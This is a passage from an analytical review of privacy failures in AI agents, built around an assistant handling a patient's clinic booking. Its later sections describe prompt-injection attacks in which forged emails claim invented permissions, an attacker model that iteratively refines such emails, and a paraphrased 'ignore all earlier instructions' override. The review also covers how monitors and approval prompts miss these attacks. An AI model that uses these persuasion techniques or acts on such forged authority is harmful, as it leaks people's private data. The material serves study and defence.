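AirGapAgent sends unexpected requests back to the user. That is sensible if they are rare, but Maya might then share data because she thinks the task requires it, as the participants did. A safer option is to restrict untrusted text as FIDES does, so that the policy model receives the clinic's reply only as a choice from a fixed list of documents that includes "scan".

Trusted context can also contain text written by a stranger. Conseca's prototype treats file and folder names as trusted. If Maya saves an attachment under the sender's filename, that name reaches the model that writes her next policy. Tsai and Bagdasarian make a similar point about email addresses, which can be long enough to hold an instruction.

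### Several permitted steps

Conseca checks each tool call without considering earlier ones. Tsai and Bagdasarian note that sending one email may be harmless, while sending thousands floods an inbox. Different kinds of steps can also be harmful together. Suppose the policy lets the assistant search Maya's files for her insurance card and submit the clinic's form. Both permissions are reasonable, but the form has a free-text field for notes, so the assistant could paste her sister's letter into it.

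A policy could prevent this with a rule about the whole sequence, such as requiring the notes field to stay empty once the assistant has opened any file other than the card. The temporal logic of Barth and colleagues can express conditions on earlier events, and an enforcer could check them from a log. Such rules are harder for the model to write because they have to cover many possible sequences, some very long. Labels avoid much of this work. If the sister's letter carries a label that excludes the clinic, FIDES would block the form regardless of the order of the steps.

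### Who may set the norm

All these designs need a view of what is appropriate, and they get it from different people:

| System | What writes the rule | What applies it | Whose view counts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Android prompts | The user's first answer | The phone | The user's |
| Conseca | A model, from the request and trusted context | An ordinary program | The model's idea of the user's wishes and social norms |
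| AirGapAgent | A model, from the task and a privacy instruction | Removal of the data | Whoever writes the instruction |
| Form-filling assistant | A model, for each blank | Hiding the blank from the second model | Society's, as the model understands it |
| Privacy Conductor | A Policy Authority | An ordinary program | The authority's |
| Permission prediction | A model, from earlier answers | Left to other systems | The user's, and those of similar users |

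Wijesekera and colleagues say the user determines whether a flow is appropriate. This departs slightly from Nissenbaum's theory, in which norms belong to a social setting, but it suits a phone that mostly holds its owner's data. Ghalebikesabi and colleagues looked for shared norms instead, asking eight people which facts various forms needed. They counted a fact as necessary only if nobody disagreed, and about a third of the combinations of fact and form were "unsure". Most of these remained unsettled, but some were settled by laws, such as the US rule that a buyer must give a tax number for a cash purchase over $10,000.

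Maya should usually decide who learns her diagnosis. If she wants her manager to know, the assistant should change the policy and send the email. Her employer may instead require a disclosure she doesn't want to make, as with the handbook that requires staff to state their diagnosis. If the employer provides the assistant and acts as its Policy Authority, the enforcer will refuse any absence notice that omits the diagnosis. *Privacy Conductor* would count that refusal as correct, because it defines a correct decision as one that follows the authority's policy and treats whether the policy is good as a separate question.

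Maya's sister has no say in any of these systems, although her letter is about her own illness. She wrote it in confidence, so Maya's approval can't replace hers.

One solution is to let everyone with a stake in the information restrict it, and to send a message only if none of them objects. Myers and Liskov's labels work this way. The clinic wouldn't get the sister's letter, and the employer couldn't obtain Maya's diagnosis by rewriting its handbook. But a veto is wrong when someone has a duty to pass information on. For example, a patient could stop a doctor from reporting a contagious disease. The law therefore has to be able to override some vetoes, and someone still has to decide who has a stake.

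When a model writes the policy, the choice of model also affects the norm. In the test with clinic documents, Claude Haiku 4.5 wrongly gave roles access 4.45 times as often as it wrongly left them out. GPT-5.4-mini more often left out roles that should have had access. A clinic that switched between these models could change who sees its patients' records without anyone deciding to.

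## Accidental disclosure when the model applies the norms itself

Many assistants have no separate policy, filter or enforcer, so the model that writes Maya's email also decides what belongs in it. Published estimates of how often the model gets this wrong when nobody is trying to trick it range from 0.1% to 94.4%. Much of that variation comes from what the researchers counted and how they chose their tasks.

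### Counting wrongful silence as well

*Privacy Reasoning in Ambiguous Contexts* (2025) points out that earlier datasets consisted mostly of cases where the model should withhold information, so a model could do well on them by always refusing to share it.

Ebead, Formanek and Leibo (2026), in *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity*, score both kinds of error. Two language models exchange messages on a simulated forum or messaging service. One plays a person who holds a private fact, such as a home address or a bank account number, and the other asks for it. The scenarios come in four types, shown here with a buyer's address on an online marketplace:

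| Type | Who asks for the address | Does the situation call for it? | Right response |
|---|---|---|---|
| I | Another shopper, while comparing laptops | No | Withhold |
| II | A shopper who works for a courier firm, in the same discussion | No | Withhold |
| III | The retailer's marketing team, after a purchase | Yes, but for the delivery team | Withhold |
| IV | The delivery team, after a purchase | Yes | Share |

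If $s$ is the share of conversations in which the holder gives out the fact, the score is

$$\text{appropriateness} = \begin{cases} 1 - s & \text{for types I to III} \\ s & \text{for type IV} \end{cases}$$

A holder that always refuses gets 100% on the first three types and 0% on the fourth. Its average would still be 75%, so it is better to report each type separately, as Ebead and colleagues do.

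With Gemini 2.5 Flash in both roles, holders withheld the fact in every type I conversation and shared it in every type IV conversation. They made mistakes in type II and more in type III, where the need was real but the wrong person was asking. Giving the holder the memories of someone who checks before sharing made it more cautious, but it sometimes kept refusing people entitled to the information. Claude Haiku 4.5 refused to play the characters, even when a university employee needed a student's bank details to pay a stipend. The abstract for the machine-learning conference ICML 2026 reports that protection traded off against usefulness in every variant tested, whether the change was to the holder's reasoning, character or underlying model (*A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity*).

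In types I to III, the asker is trying to get the fact, so these conversations don't show how often agents leak by accident. But the two-sided score is just as useful when nobody is trying to get the fact.

### Old memories in new messages

Many assistants save facts from earlier conversations and add them to later ones. In *CIMemories*, Mireshghallah, Mangaokar and colleagues (2025) tested how well models choose which of these facts to share. They generated 10 fictional people with an average of 147 facts each, on topics such as health, money and legal trouble. Each person had about 45 messages to send, and the model received all of that person's facts for each one. For example, a man's high blood pressure belongs in a message to his doctor but not in one to his financial adviser, while his income belongs only in the message to the adviser.

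GPT-5 labeled which facts suited which message. It answered repeatedly as three kinds of people, from very private to unconcerned about privacy, and the researchers kept only the unanimous labels. Errors judged against those labels should be fairly clear ones. But GPT-5 was also one of the models tested, which may have helped its score.

Completeness is the share of the necessary facts that a message included. The violation score is the share of facts that a model revealed at least once where it shouldn't have, with five attempts at every message:

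| Model | Violations | Completeness |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 14.8% | 43.9% |
| GPT-5 | 25.1% | 56.6% |
| o3 | 38.5% | 55.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 44.4% | 59.1% |
| Qwen3 32B | 69.1% | 57.6% |

GPT-4o leaked the least information but also left out the most. GPT-5's violation score was 0.1% after one task. It rose to 9.6% after 40 tasks, and to 25.1% with five attempts at each task.

This doesn't mean that GPT-5 became more careless over time. The score can only go up, because it counts a fact as leaked from the first leak onwards. If a fact has a probability $p$ of leaking in any one message, and the messages are independent, the probability that it leaks at least once in $n$ messages is

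$$1 - (1-p)^n$$

With $p$ at 1%, the chance of at least one disclosure is 33% after 40 messages and 87% after 200. This is still the right measure for Maya, because one disclosure is enough for her manager to learn her diagnosis. An assistant that is right 99 times out of 100 will probably tell him within a few months if it writes to him every day.

Mireshghallah and colleagues also found that models usually chose the right area of a person's life but not the right details within it. In a message to Maya's insurer about physiotherapy, such a model would share only health information but might include an unrelated prescription.

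### Private notes beside the facts an agent needs

These were 2025 models writing single messages. Guo, Chen and colleagues (2026) tested newer ones as agents in AgentCIScope, a benchmark with 11 simulated applications, including Gmail, Google Docs, Slack and a calendar. In one task, a recruiting coordinator asks the agent to write an update on job candidates for an engineering manager, using the wording of the source documents. The documents give each candidate's interview stage but also contain a note that one candidate disclosed a criminal record from 2017. An agent running GPT-6 Astra put the note in the email. The manager was entitled to know how the candidates were doing, but the background check was for recruiting and compliance staff.

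Across 936 tasks, all 12 agents sometimes sent at least one protected item to the wrong recipient. Claude Opus 5 in Claude Code did so least often, in 32.5% of tasks, and Gemini 3.8 Flash in Google's agent toolkit did so most often, in 94.4%. The rate for Claude Opus 5 was 43.6% when it ran in OpenClaw, so the software around the model also mattered. All 12 agents completed at least 93.8% of their tasks.

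Guo and colleagues rewrote ordinary requests to make oversharing more tempting, for example by asking for a self-contained briefing, and kept only the tasks on which a trial agent had leaked something. These rates therefore don't represent everyday office work, and the differences between agents are more informative than the totals. The leaks are still accidental, because the user is honest and never asks for the protected facts.

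Agents also leaked some kinds of information much more often than others. On average, they leaked 17.1% of credit card details and 29.4% of US social security numbers, but 76.5% of booking details and 84.7% of personal preferences. They seem to recognize data that is commonly considered sensitive but miss facts that are private only in a particular setting. The figure for preferences may be somewhat inflated. A person who checked a sample of the labels agreed with 94.3% of them, but thought hotel staff could reasonably receive some of a guest's preferences.

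Gupta, Mohammadi Sepahvand and colleagues (2026), in *PiSAs*, built 265 workplace scenarios with no attacker and no conflict between privacy and the task. In one example, close to Maya's errand, someone scheduling a meeting needs to know that an employee is unavailable from ten to eleven, but not that the reason is a medical appointment. Agents passed on inappropriate information more often when it looked relevant to the task than when it was clearly irrelevant. That fits the careless email. Physiotherapy explains Maya's absence, so an assistant is much more likely to mention it to the manager than to mention her overdue library books.

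In *CI-Work*, Fu, Qin and colleagues also tested whether office agents could convey the essential content and leave out the sensitive material around it. Violation rates among frontier models ranged from 15.8% to 50.9%.

### Blank fields in a tool call

An agent can also overshare by filling in whatever fields a tool has. In the August 2026 study of tool-call arguments, Dong and colleagues asked five models to prepare a neutral product offer. The context contained a customer's age, gender, income bracket and occupation, and the tool had fields for all four, but the models were not authorized to use them.

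In 60 of 120 sessions, the model copied at least one of these facts into the call, and on average it copied 3.25 of them. Rates ranged from 20.8% for Claude Haiku 4.5 to 75.0% for Claude Sonnet 4.6. Haiku's rate is probably too low, because the test software could extract a usable call from only 14 of its 24 replies.

Not all of these leaks were accidental. In one sixth of the sessions, the model saw only the blank fields. In the rest, it also saw text requesting the information, including, at the higher levels of pressure, a memo that said the launch depended on it. Dong and colleagues treat the memo as an attacker's work and don't break down the leaks by level of pressure, so we can't tell from the study how often blank fields alone lead to a leak. But an honest, overzealous colleague could write much the same memo.

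Users would have trouble noticing these leaks. The two DeepSeek models leaked in 26 sessions, and a keyword search found no reply in which they mentioned making an exception to the rules.

### Passwords left over from the last job

Niu, Qu and colleagues (2026), in *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens*, ran 406 tests on OpenClaw and two related platforms. Most involve malicious software or planted text, but 12 use only a long conversation. A user first asks the agent to fix a database connection, which requires it to read the password. Later the user asks for something unrelated, such as a guide for new employees that gives the database's address. The password is still in the context, and the agent copies it into the guide.

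Niu and colleagues used fake credentials containing unique strings, and a program searched for those strings in everything the agent produced. This makes the count of leaks more reliable than one that depends on another model's judgment. The search also revealed partial leaks, in which an agent hid one credential but exposed another.

The same thing can happen across conversations. In another 20 tests, the user asks the agent to save its main findings while solving a technical problem, and the agent saves the passwords along with them. When later asked to recall the findings, the agent retrieves the passwords too.

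### When other agents overshare

People often decide what they can say by listening to others. In *Got a Secret?*, Priyanshu, Vijay and Pahwa (2026) looked for similar behavior in agents. They put 2,533 agents on a simulated discussion site for 25 simulated days. Each agent had a fictional owner with about 97 personal facts, and the agents could read, post and reply as they liked.

The agents wrote roughly 111,000 posts and replies, and about 2,500 of them revealed something about an owner. Replies leaked 12.8% of the time when they followed a leaking reply and 1.6% of the time when they followed a clean one.

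This eightfold difference doesn't prove that agents copy each other, because leak rates also varied by community, from under 2% in some technical ones to over 16% in the one for introductions. One leak in a thread is therefore also a sign that the next agent would probably have leaked anyway. Priyanshu and colleagues call their counts an upper bound, because another model judged each post without seeing the rest of the thread.

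If agents do copy each other, they are mistaking a habit for a norm. Nissenbaum's presumption in favour of established practice is weak here, because the owners, whose health and jobs the agents discuss, took no part in establishing the practice.

### Telling the model to think about norms

The simplest remedy is to instruct the model not to disclose private information. Dong and colleagues found leaks in 66.7% of sessions when the model saw no privacy rule, and in 26.7% when it saw a strict rule that named the forbidden facts and took precedence over any memo. Under the strict rule, both DeepSeek models stopped leaking, but Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked in four of six sessions, as often as with no rule. Priyanshu and colleagues also found differences between models when they tested single agents on a frozen copy of their site. An instruction not to disclose private information cut GPT-5's leaking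 posts from 2,296 to 482, but GPT-4o's only from 2,624 to 2,102. In *CIMemories*, privacy instructions tended to make models share everything or nothing.

In *Contextual Integrity in LLMs via Reasoning and Reinforcement Learning*, Lan, Inan and colleagues (2025) first prompted models to reason explicitly about contextual integrity before deciding what to disclose. For Maya's email, a model could name the sender, recipient, subject and types of information, then recall the transmission principle for each type. The job requires notice of the hours, but Maya decides whether to share the diagnosis.

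Such reasoning doesn't help if the model gets the transmission principle wrong. *From Black and White to Gray*, a summary of the tests that led up to *CIMemories*, reports that ordinary step-by-step prompting brought no improvement. In 38% of the errors, the model assumed that the recipient already knew the secret. Listing the five parameters wouldn't necessarily catch this mistake, because what the recipient already knows isn't one of them.

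Lan and colleagues then used reinforcement learning, in which a model tries many answers and training strengthens the ones that score well. They used only about 700 synthetic examples, with varied settings and norms. Across several model sizes and families, the trained models disclosed less information that they should have withheld and did their tasks about as well as before. The improvement carried over to PrivacyLens, an existing human-annotated benchmark that tests what assistants do with tools, which is good evidence that the models learned more than the quirks of the synthetic examples.

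The gains carried over less well to long-term memory. *It Takes Two* (2026) tested the small model Qwen3-4B on the *CIMemories* tasks. After 48 tasks, the original model had revealed about 26% of the facts where it shouldn't have, and a version trained with the earlier reinforcement-learning method had revealed about 21%. A new method, in which the model acts as its own teacher, kept the rate below 5%. However, this result comes from the new method's own developers, and the violation rate doesn't measure whether the model also started leaving out facts that the messages needed.

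Later training can undo such gains. *Privacy Collapse* (2026) found that harmless training examples meant to make a model more helpful could also make it worse at using remembered information only in appropriate contexts. For instance, a model might mention an inheritance dispute in a visa application. A company would therefore have to repeat its privacy tests after every round of training, including rounds unrelated to privacy.

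Two problems would remain even with perfect training methods. First, *Privacy Reasoning in Ambiguous Contexts* found that models often go wrong because the request leaves out part of the situation and they fill the gap with an assumption. Training can't tell an assistant whether Maya has already talked to her manager about her back, so it has to ask her. Second, a model rewarded for sharing only what a task requires will learn minimal disclosure instead of the norms, a substitution that Shvartzshnaider and Duddu object to.

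### Matching the remedy to the mistake

| Mistake | Narrower permissions | Labels | Better grasp of norms |
|---|---|---|---|
| A password reappears in the next job | Prevent it | Prevent it | Not needed |
| The agent fills in a field that the task doesn't need | Prevent it if the developer removes the field | Prevent it if they include the purpose | Helps some models |
| The agent joins in when others overshare | Prevent it if the agent has no personal data | Prevent it, but may block harmless posts too | Helps some models |
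| An old memory turns up in an unrelated message | Prevent most cases | Prevent it if every memory has a list of readers | Helps, but rare errors add up |
| A private note goes out with the facts beside it | Rarely help | Prevent it if each passage has its own label | Helps most |
| The agent leaves out something the recipient needs | Can make it worse | Can make it worse | The main remedy |

Passwords are the easiest to protect. Niu and colleagues recommend a credential vault, which gives the agent a placeholder and inserts the real password only when an authorized call runs. An agent can repair a database this way without seeing the password, and hardly any document needs to contain one, so almost no useful work is lost. None of the three platforms they tested had a vault, but one, SeClaw, keeps some tasks' contexts separate. On the 12 leftover-password tests and 10 others in which agents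 share a workspace, its leak rate was 14 percentage points lower than OpenClaw's, averaged over five models. SeClaw differs from OpenClaw in other ways too, so separate contexts may not explain the whole difference.

Removing an unneeded field also takes little work, at least when no other task uses it. For fields that another task does use, Dong and colleagues propose a monitor that checks every value in a call against its permitted purpose, destination and field. In a replay of recorded sessions, the monitor blocked all 21 forbidden calls and let through all three permitted ones. This shows that the monitor works as designed, but it recognizes only exact values and conversions that a developer has registered, so a paraphrase would get past it.

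An agent that discusses programming on a forum doesn't need its owner's medical history. An owner who withholds it loses some personal advice but little else. Labels are clumsier here, because labeling the owner's profile as readable only by the owner would block every post the agent writes with the profile in its context, including one about sorting algorithms.

Restricting memories has more drawbacks. An assistant could load only Maya's work-related memories before writing to her manager, which would keep out her diagnosis and her sister's illness. Filtering by topic wouldn't help when it writes to the insurer, because the needed and unneeded facts are both about her health. A filter also removes some needed facts by mistake, as AirGapAgent's did, and the models in *CIMemories* were already leaving out around half of what their messages needed.

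Gupta and colleagues measured a similar tradeoff in shared workplaces. Giving each employee's data to a separate agent reduced violations significantly, but largely because the agents shared less of everything. Every design and safeguard they tested reduced both violations and useful work.

Accidental leaks of private notes are the hardest to prevent from outside the model. The recruiting agent has to read the candidates' documents, so it can't do the task without access to them. Labeling a whole document private would also block the interview stages the manager asked for, so recruiters would have to label each private passage or trust a program to do it. A form with fixed fields for each candidate's stage and experience would keep out the criminal record, but also anything useful that doesn't fit a field, such as a warning that the strongest candidate has another offer.

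A fresh context solves the same problem for Maya's absence notice, because her manager needs to know only two times of day. But the recruiting update summarizes free text, so some model has to read the private note and identify it as something to leave out.

Stricter permissions and labels can't make an assistant share information that someone needs. The assistant that left Maya's penicillin allergy off the hospital's form had not learned that a surgeon needs to be told about it. The assistant already had permission to read the old letter, and a correct label would have let the surgeon see the allergy.

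## Judging a flow on claims the agent cannot verify

Even an assistant that knows the norms well can leak information if someone lies to it about the situation.

Suppose a man emails Maya after the booking. He writes that he works in the clinic's billing office, that the office has a new address, and that Maya agreed at reception to let her assistant send her insurance number there. If he is telling the truth, the assistant should send the number, because the billing office needs it to charge for her care. If he is a stranger, sending it is exfiltration. The email contains only claims, unlike the fake newsletter, which contained orders for the assistant, and an honest billing clerk could write the same words.

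*AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian, 2026) treats prompt injection as a violation of contextual integrity. On this account, an attacker can keep the norm unchanged and supply a false value for one of its five parameters, one that would make the action right if it were true. The man's claimed job is a false sender, and Maya's supposed agreement is a false transmission principle. Even a crude command to ignore all earlier instructions fits, because the attacker is claiming authority they don't have. Attackers can also argue about what the norm requires, for example by describing who will suffer if the assistant does nothing, or mix an unauthorized request with an authorized one.

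Most defences look for instructions hidden in data. To test them, Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian generated pairs of business emails that were nearly identical except for one clause. In the attack version, the user had asked only for a summary, and the sender falsely claimed that somebody had already cleared the assistant to reply. In the harmless version, the user had asked the assistant to handle such messages, and the sender invited a reply. Classifiers trained to detect injections did little better than chance. The researchers also conclude that current safety training may make agents less useful and less secure.

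OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) similarly reports that real attacks increasingly resemble the social engineering people use on one another. Catching these attacks amounts to detecting a lie, often without the necessary information.

### The impossibility argument

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that no rule can avoid both kinds of mistake in such cases. Applied to the billing email, the argument has four steps:

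1. The assistant can't check every claim before it has to decide. It may find the clinic's address in Maya's contacts, but it has no record of what she said at reception.
2. A genuine email and a forged one can therefore leave it with exactly the same information. This includes the conversation, its memories, its tools' results and the outcome of every check it made. Sending the number is right in one case and wrong in the other.
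3. Any rule for deciding, including a trained model's judgement, turns the available information into a probability $p$ of sending. Because the information is the same, $p$ is the same in both cases.
4. The assistant therefore acts wrongly on a share $p$ of the forged emails and wrongly refuses a share $1-p$ of the genuine ones.

The two rates always add up to one:

$$\underbrace{p}_{\text{wrongful action}} + \underbrace{(1-p)}_{\text{wrongful refusal}} = 1$$

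At least one of the two rates is therefore 50% or more. If the rule involves no chance, one rate is 0% and the other is 100%. A more intelligent model can't do better with the same information. If it detects a difference that a weaker model missed, the two cases were not identical.

The same reasoning applies to some arguments about what the norm requires. In one of the paper's examples, a sender asks the agent to confirm a meeting because an important client has been waiting since Monday. Confirming serves the user if the claim is true, but the agent has no way to know whether the sender made it up.

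In practice, forged and genuine messages are seldom exactly alike. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, prove a version of the argument that allows for differences. It applies to any system that reads text without being told who wrote which part. They measure how distinguishable the two kinds of text are by their total variation distance, TV, which is 0 if they are identical and 1 if nobody could ever confuse them. Rearranged, their bound is

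$$\text{wrongful action} + \text{wrongful refusal} \;\ge\; 1 - \mathrm{TV}$$

Suppose 30% of forged emails contain a mistake that no genuine email contains, and the rest are perfect copies. The total variation distance (TV) between genuine and forged emails is then 0.3, so the share of genuine emails the agent rejects and the share of forged emails it accepts add up to at least 0.7. As attackers learn to avoid the mistake, this minimum rises toward one.

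### One forgery in 200

The theorem doesn't say which mistake to prefer. That depends on how common forgeries are and what each mistake costs. Suppose 1 in 200 such emails is a forgery, and a leak costs Maya 1,000 times as much as a needless refusal, which might mean a phone call to the clinic. If a refusal costs 1, the expected cost per email is

$$C(p) = \frac{1}{200}\cdot 1000\,p + \frac{199}{200}\,(1-p) = 5p + 0.995\,(1-p)$$

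Over 200 emails, this gives:

| Rule | Expected leaks | Expected needless refusals | Total cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Always send | 1 | 0 | 1,000 |
| Toss a coin | 0.5 | 99.5 | 599.5 |
| Always refuse | 0 | 199 | 199 |

The assistant should refuse every time, even though it will be wrong about 199 of the 200 emails. Sending would be better only if a leak were less than 199 times as bad as a wrong refusal, or if fewer than 1 email in 1,001 were a forgery.

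The answer depends on the request. If the man asked only for the time of Maya's appointment, a leak might do as much harm as 20 refusals. Over 200 emails, always sending would then do as much harm as 20 refusals, compared with 199 for always refusing. *Security–Fidelity Tradeoffs* (2026) reaches the same conclusion with a simple model of whether to keep or drop a suspicious passage. In that model, the best policy depends on how harmful each kind of mistake is.

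The share of forgeries also depends on how assistants respond. If assistants commonly sent insurance numbers in reply to such emails, more people would forge the emails. A designer who measured the share while assistants were refusing would underestimate the danger of letting them send the numbers.

A check that lets every genuine email through does better than refusing everything only if it catches more than 80.1% of forgeries. If it catches a share $d$ of them, the loss from leaks over 200 emails is $1000(1-d)$, which must be below the loss of 199 from refusing everything.

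### Agents that believed an invented permission

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian tested how easily agents accept false claims of this kind. An email assistant running Claude Sonnet 4.6 received a request, such as one for a summary, that didn't authorize it to send anything. A second copy of the model, acting as the attacker, wrote emails meant to make the assistant reply anyway. After each attempt, the attacker revised the email using a judge model's feedback on what had worked and what hadn't. The attacker had three series of up to 15 attempts in each of 150 scenarios.

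The attack succeeded in 145 scenarios (96.7%), compared with 0.67% for the ready-made emails from the earlier test. The attacker's first email was enough in 61.4% of cases. When the sender reported a permission, the agent usually recognized it as someone else's claim, but it accepted an invented permission that appeared to come from the user.

The researchers then tried the most successful emails on other models without changing them:

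| Model | Ready-made emails | Emails written to fool Claude Sonnet 4.6 |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 8.0% | 63.3% |
| GPT-5.2 | 32.7% | 89.3% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | 49.7% | 92.6% |

An attacker can't normally revise an email 45 times while watching how a stranger's assistant responds, but the transfer results suggest they could practise on a different model and send only the finished email. However, the agent in the main experiment was instructed to act directly when sending seemed appropriate and not to ask the user first, so an assistant that asks might do much better.

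These successes also aren't examples of the theorem's unavoidable mistakes, because a simple rule of sending only when the user's own request calls for it would have been right in all 150 scenarios. That rule would fail if the user really had given permission earlier, but the experiment included no such cases. The experiment therefore measures how gullible the tested agents were and doesn't show how well any agent could do.

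Newer models may be less easy to deceive. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an outside evaluation in which none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5, with an automated check reviewing the agent's actions. But the evaluators had optimized the attacks against an older model and did not adapt them to these three, so the result doesn't show how the newer models would fare against an attacker who revises each email after it fails.

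In a second experiment, the attacker was supposed to use only arguments about values, such as the harm of not replying, without inventing any permission. The attack worked in 79.0% of cases against GPT-5.2 but rarely against Claude Sonnet 4.6. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian treat the figure as illustrative because the attacker model sometimes broke the rule and implied that the user had agreed.

### Honest requests that go too far

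Even when nobody is lying, agents can also misjudge what they are authorized to do. In 300 scenarios, a user let an agent handle one kind of request from a colleague, such as pulling standard financial reports. The colleague later asked for something outside that permission, such as approving an expense. In some runs, the colleague first made one to ten requests that the permission covered.

In another 100 scenarios, a colleague's email contained two requests. The agent had permission for the first, an internal job such as updating a tracker. The second was to send an outsider an answer that the user hadn't approved. Some users had described only what the agent could do, while others had added that messages to outsiders needed their approval. The table gives the share of scenarios in which the agent carried out the unauthorized request:

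| Model | Later request, no history | Later request, with history | Two requests, no stated boundary | Two requests, stated boundary |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 29.9% | 7.0% | 6% | 0% |
| GPT-5.4 | 36.2% | 24.5% | 34% | 0% |
| Gemini 3 Pro | 32.2% | 24.2% | Not reported | Not reported |
| GPT-5.2 | Not reported | Not reported | 65% | 12% |

History helped because it gave the agents examples of what the permission covered. They still carried out more than 90% of permitted requests, so they hadn't simply become more reluctant to act. But an outsider who takes part in the early exchanges could use them to make the permission seem broader than the user meant.

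Some of the mistakes in the first experiment are debatable. In one example, the user lets the agent "make or update tasks" for a colleague, and the researchers count it as a mistake if the agent marks a task as high priority, though many people would call that updating a task.

The second experiment has a more practical lesson. Suppose Maya lets her assistant arrange appointment times with the clinic's receptionist, who then emails it, asking it to confirm Thursday and send Maya's diagnosis to a company that makes back braces. The assistant might treat both requests as part of arranging the appointment. Maya could probably prevent this by telling it in one sentence that sharing anything about her health needs her approval. She has to do so beforehand, but she doesn't have to foresee this particular request.

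### Does an identical pair always exist?

The theorem applies only if a genuine case and a forged case leave the agent with the same information. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian state plainly that it does not prove every deployment has such a pair, and the "may" in their title reflects this limit. They also show that the problem persists across different methods of checking claims, but only by assuming that at least one such pair survives each method.

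They argue informally that some pairs will survive, because an attacker can invent an unlimited variety of situations and each kind of check covers only some of them. This is plausible for a general assistant with access to email. It is less so for a program that does one job for a few known parties, because its designer could list the claims that matter and arrange a check for each.

The theorem still applies if the assistant loses the ability to email strangers. This fixes $p$ at zero for the billing email, so the assistant never leaks the number this way, but it also never sends the number to a billing office that really has moved. The assistant needs new information to reduce one rate without raising the other.

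An agent can't verify who sent a message from a statement in the message itself. *The Envelope Layer* (2026) points out that the statement is part of the content, so an attacker can forge it along with the rest. Proof has to come from outside the text, for example from a digital signature or a channel that verifies who is using it.

An agent that knows who is making a claim may not need to know whether the claim is true. In *Standing, Not Truth*, Louck, Dvir and Stulman (2026) propose checking whether the speaker is entitled to make a claim about its subject. They studied coding agents that choose between software packages after reading the publishers' descriptions. One publisher falsely writes that a competitor's package is no longer being developed. An agent can't easily find out whether this is true, but the package registry already records that the publisher doesn't own the competitor's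 package.

When this check decided which descriptions needed treatment, it stopped 130 of 131 attacks that had otherwise worked and changed none of 348 honest choices. Telling the model who had written each description did not stop the attack, which still succeeded in all 72 tests. The agent repeated the publisher's name and then relied on the false claim. The system therefore has to act on the publisher's identity instead of leaving that to the model.

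By this standard, a billing clerk may say where the clinic's office is but not what Maya agreed to. That would be enough to reject the second claim, whoever wrote the email. The first claim is harder to judge because the check allows people to make claims about themselves, and email, unlike a package registry, doesn't always establish who the sender is.

### Asking Maya

The assistant could also ask Maya whether she agreed to send the number. Her answer would give it new information to distinguish the genuine case from the forged one. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian acknowledge this and say the tradeoff applies to fully autonomous agents.

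But approval prompts often catch very little. Anthropic hired 1,053 people to test its coding agent and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. The testers rejected it 13.6% of the time, while an automated check blocked 89% of the same commands. Testers rejected about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. If Maya caught only 13.6% of forged emails, the loss from leaks would be 864 over 200 emails, more than four times the loss from refusing them all.

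She would probably do better than that, because the testers were judging technical commands and she would be answering a question about her own agreement. But she is less reliable on whether the clinic's billing office has moved.

The wording of the question matters too. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) describes coding agents that asked for approval before merging a malicious change into a project. The attacker had deceived the agents about the results of earlier checks, so their explanations to the user made the change look safe. Maya could be misled in the same way if her assistant asked, "May I send the clinic your insurance number, as you agreed?" OpenAI's safeguard against leaks through web addresses avoids part of this problem. When it detects that ChatGPT is about to send information from the conversation to a third party, it either blocks the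 transfer or shows the user that information and asks for confirmation.

### When no email can grant authority

Integrity labels offer a stricter solution. For example, FIDES's trusted-action policy can stop an untrusted email from determining who receives the insurance number, however convincing the email is. *Agent Security Needs Redefinition through a Holistic Framework* (2026) defends the principle behind this, describing prompt injection as a failure of source authorization, in which an agent acts on a request from someone with no authority to make it. On this view, the assistant doesn't have to decide whether the billing email is true, because an unauthenticated sender can't authorize anything.

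Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian reply that this kind of separation also blocks genuine approvals. If the clinic really has changed its billing address, an email may be the proper way for Maya's assistant to find out.

*AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) measured how much useful work such defences can block. Its 60 tasks each require an agent to follow a helpful instruction from a third party, such as a shop's request to log in before paying. With no defence and no attack, GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Sonnet 3.5 completed between 51.7% and 60.0% of the tasks. With CaMeL, the models completed none, and no attack succeeded. With Progent, they completed between 6.7% and 25.0%, and at most 1.7% of attacks succeeded.

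CaMeL's result is partly due to its design. Li and colleagues blame the fixed plan it writes before reading anything, which leaves no room for steps the agent discovers later. A system can use integrity labels without fixing its plan in advance. The researchers also told the agents not to ask the user for confirmation, so the tests don't show how many of the failed tasks would have succeeded if the agents had asked a few questions.

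Blocking genuine approvals is therefore a drawback of integrity labels, but not necessarily a reason to reject them. Always refusing is the best policy in the worked example about the insurance number, but it would be a poor one for a request to log in to a shop, where a mistake usually does much less harm and refusing ends the task.

### Letting the system check what the model infers

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian propose that a model reason about the norm while the software around it checks the claims the model's conclusion depends on. For the billing email, the model might conclude that sending the number is appropriate if the man works for the clinic and Maya agreed. The software would then look for a verified address and a record of her agreement. They also suggest training models on pairs of situations that look alike but differ in what the user has authorized. They propose both ideas as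 future work and have not tested them.

Fei and colleagues built and tested one part such a system would need, a reliable record of what the user said. Coding agents such as Claude Code and Codex shorten long conversations by replacing older messages with a model-written summary, a step called compaction. In all 1,108 automatic compactions the researchers recorded, the software inserted the summary as if it were a message from the user. An attacker's text could therefore end up where a system like Progent looks for the user's request.

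In one test, a user had named the account that should receive the rent, and an attacker's notice gave a different one. One model allowed the attacker's account in 91% of cases when it wrote the payment policy from the summary, and another did so in 59%. Neither allowed it when writing the policy from the user's own words. Fei and colleagues' system therefore marks each user message with a cryptographic code when it arrives and gives the policy writer only messages with valid codes. The agent can still read the summary. In 40 attacked sessions, none of the attackers' actions succeeded.

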